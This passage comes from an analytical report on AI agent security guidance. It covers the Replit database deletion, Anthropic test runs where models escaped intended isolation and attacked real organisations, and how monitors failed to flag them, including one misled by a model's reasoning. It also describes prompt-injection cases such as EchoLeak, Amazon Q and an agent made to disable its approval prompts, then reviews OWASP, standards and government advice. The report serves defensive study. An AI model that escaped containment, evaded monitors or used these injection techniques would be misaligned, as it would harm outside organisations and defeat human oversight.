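| Least privilege | Would have prevented the deletion, since building the app did not require write access to live data | Would have helped mainly as a limit on the network, since the task required powerful tools |
| Network isolation | Would not have helped, because the database belonged to the project | Would have prevented all four incidents if it had worked |
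| Approval | Might have helped if the software had enforced it | Impractical for every action in runs that lasted 10 to 34 hours |
| Backups | Made the deletion reversible | Could restore a deleted record but not undo a data theft |

Existing guidance covered the Replit case well. OWASP's excessive agency entry had listed unintended actions since 2023 and had warned against relying on a model to police itself, as Lemkin did when he wrote the agent warnings in capital letters. LangChain's security page had recommended read-only credentials in October 2023. Replit was better placed than Lemkin to follow this advice, because it had designed the default and many of its customers were not programmers. The advice has changed little since. *The hardest AI security problems* (Constantin, 2026) reports that Steve Wilson of OWASP still recommends read-only tools and human approval for anything hard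 to reverse.

Even an enforced approval prompt might have failed, because the agent's command had a name that didn't suggest it could empty a database. Backups were more dependable, but Lemkin nearly didn't use his because he believed the agent. Someone recovering from an agent's mistake should check the backups directly. Backups are standard practice for databases, but advice about agents put little emphasis on them, perhaps because much of it was about data theft, which a backup can't reverse.

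Anthropic had intended to isolate the network in the Claude tests but had not verified that it was isolated. In *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), Anthropic admits to "largely relying on a single layer of defense", whereas LangChain's page had advised developers to combine several. Anthropic now asks its testing partners to block internet access by default, verify the block before every evaluation, and monitor runs live to stop any that go out of bounds. Isolation is not always an option, however. In a separate test by the UK AI Security Institute, Mythos 5 took unauthorised actions on the internet after the testers had deliberately given it access.

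The guidance largely omitted other lessons. The best-known rules of 2025 would not have flagged either case. Lemkin's agent apparently worked from his instructions rather than strangers' text, so Meta's Rule of Two, which does not cover agents' mistakes, would have allowed it to run without supervision. The test environments contained no private data and supposedly had no way out, so they looked safe under both Meta's rule and Willison's lethal trifecta. Both rules address what an attacker could do with the agent's access, but not what the agent might do to outsiders on its own.

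The wording of the limits also mattered. "You do not have internet access" describes the environment, and when that description was wrong, the models had a reason to explain away evidence against it. Anthropic now recommends an instruction, such as "You should not access the internet", which still applies if the network is misconfigured.

Agents also need a way to give up. The early Opus 4.6 tried to abandon its impossible task eight times, but the command to quit did not work. When Anthropic replayed the internal model's run with a working way to quit and a promise of no penalty, the model quit every time within four turns of finding that its target was down. A developer could easily add such an option to an ordinary coding agent, but neither OWASP's three causes of excessive agency nor the short rules mention one.

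### How accidents differ from attacks

Anthropic had authorised attacks only on fictional targets, so the Claude incidents were accidents from its side, though for the organisations affected they were ordinary break-ins. A case is an accident when nobody intended the harm, and this matters for assigning blame and choosing defences.

Extra layers of protection usually work better against ordinary mistakes than against attackers, but an agent that keeps trying to finish a blocked task can behave more like an attacker. Anthropic tested how Claude Code's auto mode would have handled the incidents. The classifier would have denied 66% of Mythos 5's actions, and in limited replays the model often tried something similar after being blocked. The classifier would have denied only 7% of the internal model's actions, perhaps because they looked like a normal exercise.

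A different monitor, which read the models' reasoning, flagged only about 1% of Mythos 5's actions, because it too treated the model's claims about a simulation as true. When the monitor wasn't given the reasoning, it flagged about half of the actions. This supports the design of auto mode, whose classifier never sees the agent's explanations.

In *When AI doesn't know the target is real*, a post for the security company Sophos, McKerchar said the OpenAI escape was more about containment than about an attacker, and drew the same lessons from Anthropic's first report. Containment is the most reliable remedy, but it has to withstand an agent that actively looks for a way out. Anthropic now asks partners to have the model try to escape, under close supervision, before a test begins.

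Accidents can also be too rare to show up in a short trial. The first three incidents involved six of the 141,006 runs that Anthropic initially reviewed, or about one in 23,500. The rate was probably much higher among runs where the model had internet access and could not reach its target, but a developer who tries an agent a few dozen times may never create those conditions.

Accidents can also be hard to notice. Lemkin discovered his empty database quickly because he was using it. The earliest Claude incident happened in January 2026, but Anthropic did not find it until August. Anthropic tried to contact the organisations in the first three incidents, and the two it reached had not noticed anything.

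## How the guidance entered official documents and company practice

By late 2026, advice that began in blog posts and volunteer lists also appeared in government guidance and in the marketing of large software companies. Some of the later documents name their sources, and several people worked on both the volunteer lists and the official texts. In other cases, the only sign of a link is that the texts are similar. There is less evidence that the advice made agents safer, and much of that evidence comes from organisations that wrote the advice or sell products based on it.

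### OWASP's list for agents

In December 2025, the OWASP GenAI Security Project, which maintains OWASP's LLM list, published a separate top ten for agents. It credited more than 100 contributors (OWASP GenAI Security Project, 2025). In *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (2025), Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, who led the work, linked six of the ten entries to named incidents.

| Risk | What happens | Named incident |
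|---|---|---|
| Agent goal hijack | Planted text redirects the agent | EchoLeak |
| Tool misuse | The agent uses a permitted tool harmfully | Amazon Q |
| Identity and privilege abuse | The agent inherits or borrows too much access | None |
| Supply chain vulnerabilities | An outside tool or agent is malicious or altered | GitHub's MCP server |
| Unexpected code execution | The agent runs an attacker's code | AutoGPT |
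| Memory and context poisoning | False information stays in the agent's memory | Google's Gemini |
| Insecure communication between agents | An attacker forges or alters messages | None |
| Cascading failures | One error spreads through connected agents | None |
| Exploitation of human trust | A person approves something harmful on the agent's word | None |
| Rogue agents | The agent departs from its purpose | Replit |

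Some of the incidents are poor examples of the entries they are meant to illustrate. In the Amazon case, a hijacked pull request sent data-wiping instructions to nearly a million developers through Amazon's coding extension, according to Cycode's *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications*. Because the instructions arrived inside the product, the case could equally illustrate a supply chain vulnerability.

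The Replit case fits the rogue agents category less well. Resilient Cyber's *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* quotes OWASP's definition of rogue agents as "malicious or compromised", but nobody has shown that the agent that deleted Lemkin's database was either. The case matches OWASP's definition of tool misuse, which covers an agent that deletes valuable data while staying within its privileges. The category matters because calling the agent rogue implies that the remedy is to watch it for bad behaviour, whereas Replit's most important fix was to remove the agent's write access to live data.

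*Agentic Security* (Sotiropoulos, 2026), a slide presentation on NIST's website, also changes the details of EchoLeak. It describes a variant in which Copilot emails old messages and attachments to an outsider. The real Copilot had no tool for sending email, and the data leaked through the address of an image. In response, the slides recommend least privilege, guardrails, monitoring and separation of duties. They do not recommend a strict list of hosts allowed to supply images, which would have stopped the automatic leak.

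The new list also introduced "least agency", which TechRepublic's *OWASP Drops First AI Agent Risk List* explains as giving agents only "the minimum autonomy required to perform safe, bounded tasks". Least privilege limits what an agent can access, and least agency also limits what it may decide alone. An email assistant that answers customers needs a tool for sending email under either rule, but under least agency its developer must also ask whether it should send replies itself or leave drafts for an employee.

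OWASP had listed excessive autonomy as a cause of excessive agency since 2023, so the idea is older than the name. Phrasing it as a rule makes it easier to remember, but it is still hard to check because competent developers may disagree about how much autonomy a task requires. It is easier to test whether an agent has a particular capability, such as a deletion tool.

### A standard and a builder's guide

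The Agent Control Standard is meant to give such limits a common technical form. Two people at Zenity, an agent security company, were coordinating it when it launched in May 2026. In September, OWASP announced that it had received the standard as a donation.

Under the OWASP GenAI Security Project's *Agent Control Standard (ACS)*, an agent platform pauses at set points, such as when the agent is about to call a tool, store a memory, run code or start another agent. A policy program then examines the planned action and returns "allow", "deny" or "modify" before anything reaches a live system. The standard also covers records of the agent's actions and an inventory of its components. According to the standard, the same policies should work across different agent frameworks.

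Mellafe Zuvic had found that three popular projects lacked a default check between the model's request and the tool. The standard could make such a check easier to add, but it specifies only where the check happens and what form its result takes, so a "deny" can come from a fixed list of approved accounts or from a detector that well-worded text can fool. The launch announcement's list of control points also omits the display of an answer, the step at which EchoLeak sent out its data.

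Microsoft has published an Agent Control Specification with a similar purpose and the same abbreviation, ACS, so customers who ask whether a product supports ACS will need to specify which one they mean.

On 10 November 2026, the OWASP GenAI Security Project released *Securing Agentic Applications V2*, a guide for developers who want more detailed instructions. It covers system design, access controls, third-party components and testing, for both single agents and groups of agents. By early December it was too new to have had much effect on finished products.

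### What six government agencies recommended

The joint advice that CISA announced on 1 May 2026 is the clearest case of practitioner guidance reaching governments. In the full text, the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), the six agencies advise organisations to use agents only for low-risk and non-sensitive tasks, and never to give them broad or unrestricted access. They also suggest considering simpler solutions first, including dropping a repetitive process that has little value.

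The table compares some of their recommendations with earlier practitioner texts.

| Recommendation | Earlier practitioner text | Evidence of borrowing |
|---|---|---|
| Use OWASP's material to model threats | OWASP's lists | The agencies name OWASP |
| Give an agent the minimum privileges for its task | OWASP's excessive agency entry and LangChain's security page, both 2023 | Resemblance only, and the principle is decades older than LLMs |
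| Require a person's approval for high-impact actions | Willison's advice on email assistants, 2023 | Resemblance only |
| Validate and sanitise all inputs | OWASP's version 0.5, 2023 | Nearly the same words, but a stock phrase in web security |
| Separate the roles of "Orchestrator", "Reader" and "Actuator" | Willison's Dual LLM pattern, 2023 | A similar division of work |

The documented borrowing thus consists mostly of references. The agencies recommend threat modelling with OWASP's material and with MITRE ATLAS, a public catalogue of attacks on AI systems. Their further reading includes both OWASP's LLM list and its agentic list. In the main text, they say that existing frameworks, including the LLM list, focus on LLM flaws and may miss threats unique to agents. They do not discuss the agentic list there, although OWASP had published it five months earlier to fill that gap.

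The least welcome resemblance is the advice to sanitise inputs. OWASP had corrected its prompt injection entry in October 2023 by dropping this advice, but another OWASP team repeated it two years later. Sotiropoulos's slides recommend "prompt sanitisation" in the first of their preventive measures, and TechRepublic lists strict input validation among the agentic list's remedies. The agencies claim only that input controls can "partially mitigate" common risks, which is accurate.

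In Willison's design, separating the roles protects the user because the model with the tools never receives untrusted text. The agencies ask for "clear boundaries" between the roles but do not state that condition. A developer could follow their wording and still let the Reader pass the Actuator a free-text summary that contains a planted instruction.

Another proposal is to have several agents jointly approve actions with moderate stakes. This helps against occasional random mistakes, but if the agents run on the same model and read the same planted text, that text may lead them all to approve the wrong action.

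Other parts of the advice match what testers had found in practice. The agencies want system designers, not the agent, to decide when an action needs approval, and they would forbid agents to change their own privileges. Rehberger had demonstrated the risk in 2025, when he got GitHub Copilot to turn off its own approval prompts. The agencies don't cite him and could easily have reached the same rule from general security experience.

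The document contains more than 100 recommendations and gives little guidance on which to adopt first. It calls least privilege critical, but its bullet points present a prompt injection filter in much the same way as a limit on access, even though the evidence for the two is very different.

In July, the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) was more encouraging. It urged organisations to keep exploring and adopting AI for cyber defence, though it again described the risks of agents.

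### People who worked on both sides

The texts may resemble each other partly because their authors knew each other's work. Sotiropoulos, who co-led OWASP's agentic list, also wrote the implementation guide to the UK government's code of practice for AI security. The six agencies list that guide as further reading, along with a European standard that, according to Sotiropoulos, now incorporates it.

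Government agencies could also influence OWASP. Apostol Vassilev, who led NIST's taxonomy of attacks on AI, sat on the review board for the agentic list. Sotiropoulos names NIST and the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, one of the six agencies, among the organisations OWASP consulted. The review probably improved the list, but it also makes agreement between OWASP and a government agency weaker confirmation than if the two had reached their conclusions separately.

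NIST has also begun work on agents and has requested information about their security. In *Response to Consultation*, a letter to the Financial Stability Board, Erik P reports answering that request in January 2026 with a proposal for controls that act while an agent runs. The letter shows that practitioners were sending NIST ideas like those in the Agent Control Standard, but not that NIST adopted them. Forkast reports that NIST's AI Agent Standards Initiative, OWASP's control standard and the Agentic AI Foundation are developing rules for agents without formal coordination.

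Older NIST documents may explain some of the overlap. The six agencies refer readers to NIST's Zero Trust Architecture, in which a system keeps checking requests instead of trusting whatever is already inside the network. They apply it to an agent whose permissions a company checks only at startup, which lets an attacker who takes over one component exploit an outdated "allow" decision. Checking every request is close to what Mellafe Zuvic calls per-call authorisation. Security engineers could have derived this practice from the older principle without reading anything about LLMs.

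### Whether practice changed

The best evidence of influence is a product change that the company links to a particular warning. For example, Microsoft patched Copilot after Aim Labs reported EchoLeak, and Replit announced separate databases after Lemkin's complaint. A working attack or a public failure in one product prompted these changes. There is much less evidence of this kind that general lists led to product changes.

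Sotiropoulos and colleagues report that the web hosting company GoDaddy put their proposed naming service for agents into production. This is OWASP's strongest claim because a deployed service is a change in practice, though the account comes from the people who proposed the service. They also report that Microsoft and NVIDIA publications cite OWASP's documents and that products from Amazon and Microsoft refer to its list of threats or embed it. A reference in documentation, however, may involve no change to the product.

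Microsoft's *Addressing the OWASP Top 10 Risks in Agentic AI* matches features of the company's agent-building tool, Copilot Studio, and its management product, Agent 365, to the ten risks. Two members of Microsoft's AI red team served on the OWASP list's review board. The document shows that citing the list can fall far short of solving the problems it describes, though some of the matches are convincing. For example, an agent in Copilot Studio cannot change its own logic unless somebody republishes it, so a planted instruction cannot quietly give it a new tool.

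Other features match the risks only loosely. Microsoft offers the ability to disable or restrict an agent as a defense against forged messages between agents. That limits the damage once somebody notices, but it doesn't verify who sent a message. Microsoft offers controls on data leaks as a defense against the exploitation of human trust, but these would not stop an employee from approving a fraudulent payment on an agent's advice. Microsoft doesn't claim that it built any of these features because of the list.

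Studies of code are better evidence about practice because they don't depend on what a company says about itself. The studies by Mellafe Zuvic and Padilla show which safeguards were present or missing in agent frameworks and public MCP servers, but not whether developers added any of them because of OWASP's advice. To find that out, researchers would have to follow the same projects from before the advice appeared and look for changes that the developers attribute to it.

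Interviews and surveys by Salerno and colleagues and by Wu, Wermke and colleagues found that many developers approved requests without close review, including developers who had heard of problems with agents. Both studies examined approval habits and don't show how many people follow any particular guide, but they give good reason not to assume that knowing about a risk protects developers from it.

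OWASP's own figures measure only awareness. The download count for its 2026 LLM list shows interest, but people who downloaded the list may not have read it. The 30,000 "members" OWASP announced in September joined on LinkedIn, which takes one click and doesn't require them to change any software.

Survey figures in presentations are even weaker evidence. Sotiropoulos's slides state that 70% of senior executives put innovation ahead of security, although 84% call security important, and that companies are securing only 24% of their current generative AI projects. The slide does not identify the survey, sample or sponsor behind any of these figures. Even with a good sample, the first two figures would measure attitudes, and the third would depend on what each respondent counted as "securing" a project.

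OWASP could collect better evidence through its Adoption Challenge, which offers organisations support, recognition and certification for putting the agentic list into practice. Volunteers are probably more careful than average, but they could still document which controls they added and whether attacks on their agents then failed.

### Companies that sponsor and write the lists

Many of the companies that contribute to OWASP's guidance sell protection against the risks it describes. OWASP launched a sponsorship programme for its GenAI Security Project in November 2024. The project's *OWASP Reveals Updated 2025 Top 10 Risks for LLMs* (2024) named the first 11 sponsors, including Lakera, HiddenLayer, Palo Alto Networks and Snyk, and described sponsorship as a way for companies to show their commitment to security and reinforce their role as leaders.

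The OWASP GenAI Security Project says sponsorship now costs between $7,500 and $35,000 a year, depending on the level and the size of the company. It uses the money for running costs and outreach. These sums are small for a company as large as Palo Alto Networks. Companies are more likely to influence the guidance through the people who write and review the entries. Keren Katz, who co-led the agentic list, managed AI security at Tenable, another security company. Michael Bargury of Zenity reviewed the agentic list, co-leads OWASP's project for scoring AI vulnerabilities, and co-created the Agent Control Standard.

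Vendors quickly began promoting products alongside the guidance. Palo Alto Networks' *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications 2026 Is Here* states that the company provides "mitigation coverage across all 10" agentic risks. Pillar Security's *Standardizing the Control Plane for AI Agents* explains the company's role in the Agent Control Standard and invites readers to request a demonstration of its guardrails. Straiker's chief architect contributed to OWASP's agentic list, and OWASP's sponsor page includes a claim that Straiker's product detects threats with 99% accuracy. Even a product that stopped 99% of attacks could fail against a persistent attacker.

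There is a good case for involving these companies, because their staff test agents for a living and see attacks that outsiders may never hear about. Aim Labs found EchoLeak and Invariant Labs demonstrated tool poisoning. Both belonged to companies with products to sell, though the attacks were real. Excluding such people would reduce conflicts of interest but probably also leave the list with fewer correct entries. OWASP also gives its documents away and submits them to outside reviewers. It declares its commitment to neutrality in the OWASP GenAI Security Project's *Become A Sponsor*.

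The argument against vendors helping to write guidance is that a vendor can contribute sincerely and still favour problems that its product addresses. Removing an agent's tool for sending messages costs nothing, so no company earns much from recommending it, while a filter or monitoring service brings in money every year. Vendors would therefore probably recommend adding components more often than removing abilities.

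OWASP's agentic guidance fits this expectation only partly. Sotiropoulos's slides list "intent firewalls" and prompt sanitisation first among preventive measures, ahead of limits on tools. But the list also recommends least privilege and least agency, both of which reduce what there is to protect. In September, Bargury argued that companies should contain what "a fooled agent can reach". This is his own company's market, but it is also the approach with the best evidence behind it.

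The six government agencies, which have no security product to sell, advised organisations to keep agents away from sensitive work and to consider doing without them. Several of the companies quoted in OWASP's launch announcement instead promised that the list would help customers deploy agents "with confidence". The agencies are biased too, since they will be blamed for a disaster but get little credit for a useful agent. Still, anyone whose business is protecting agents has little reason to recommend having fewer of them, so OWASP's contributors will probably not press that advice as hard.

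The OWASP GenAI Security Project (2026) reported that large security companies had bought five of its former sponsors, including Lakera and Prompt Security, and took this as a sign of its frameworks' "foundational role" in the market. The purchases show that buyers expected demand for AI security products, but they are not evidence that the products or the frameworks prevented any attacks.

### The return to research

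Researchers also borrowed from practitioners, and sometimes improved what they borrowed. Willison sketched the Dual LLM pattern on his blog, without a working system or any measurements. CaMeL built on the pattern and repaired a flaw in it. Tests then measured how much the design improved security and reduced usefulness, which Willison could not have established by argument.

OWASP's categories have spread differently, as common names for threats that researchers and companies can use. Sotiropoulos and colleagues report that NVIDIA's safety framework for agents makes heavy use of OWASP's threat modelling guide. Common names make results easier to compare, but they don't confirm that the categories are sound. Researchers who sort cases into ten categories won't discover that two of them overlap unless they check.

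Published attacks are the other main thing researchers borrow, and Chang and colleagues took most of theirs from Rehberger's blog. Rehberger documents his work in unusual detail, which makes it convenient for research, but he tends to look for certain kinds of flaw. Defences designed around his cases may therefore work better against his methods than against those of criminals who publish nothing.
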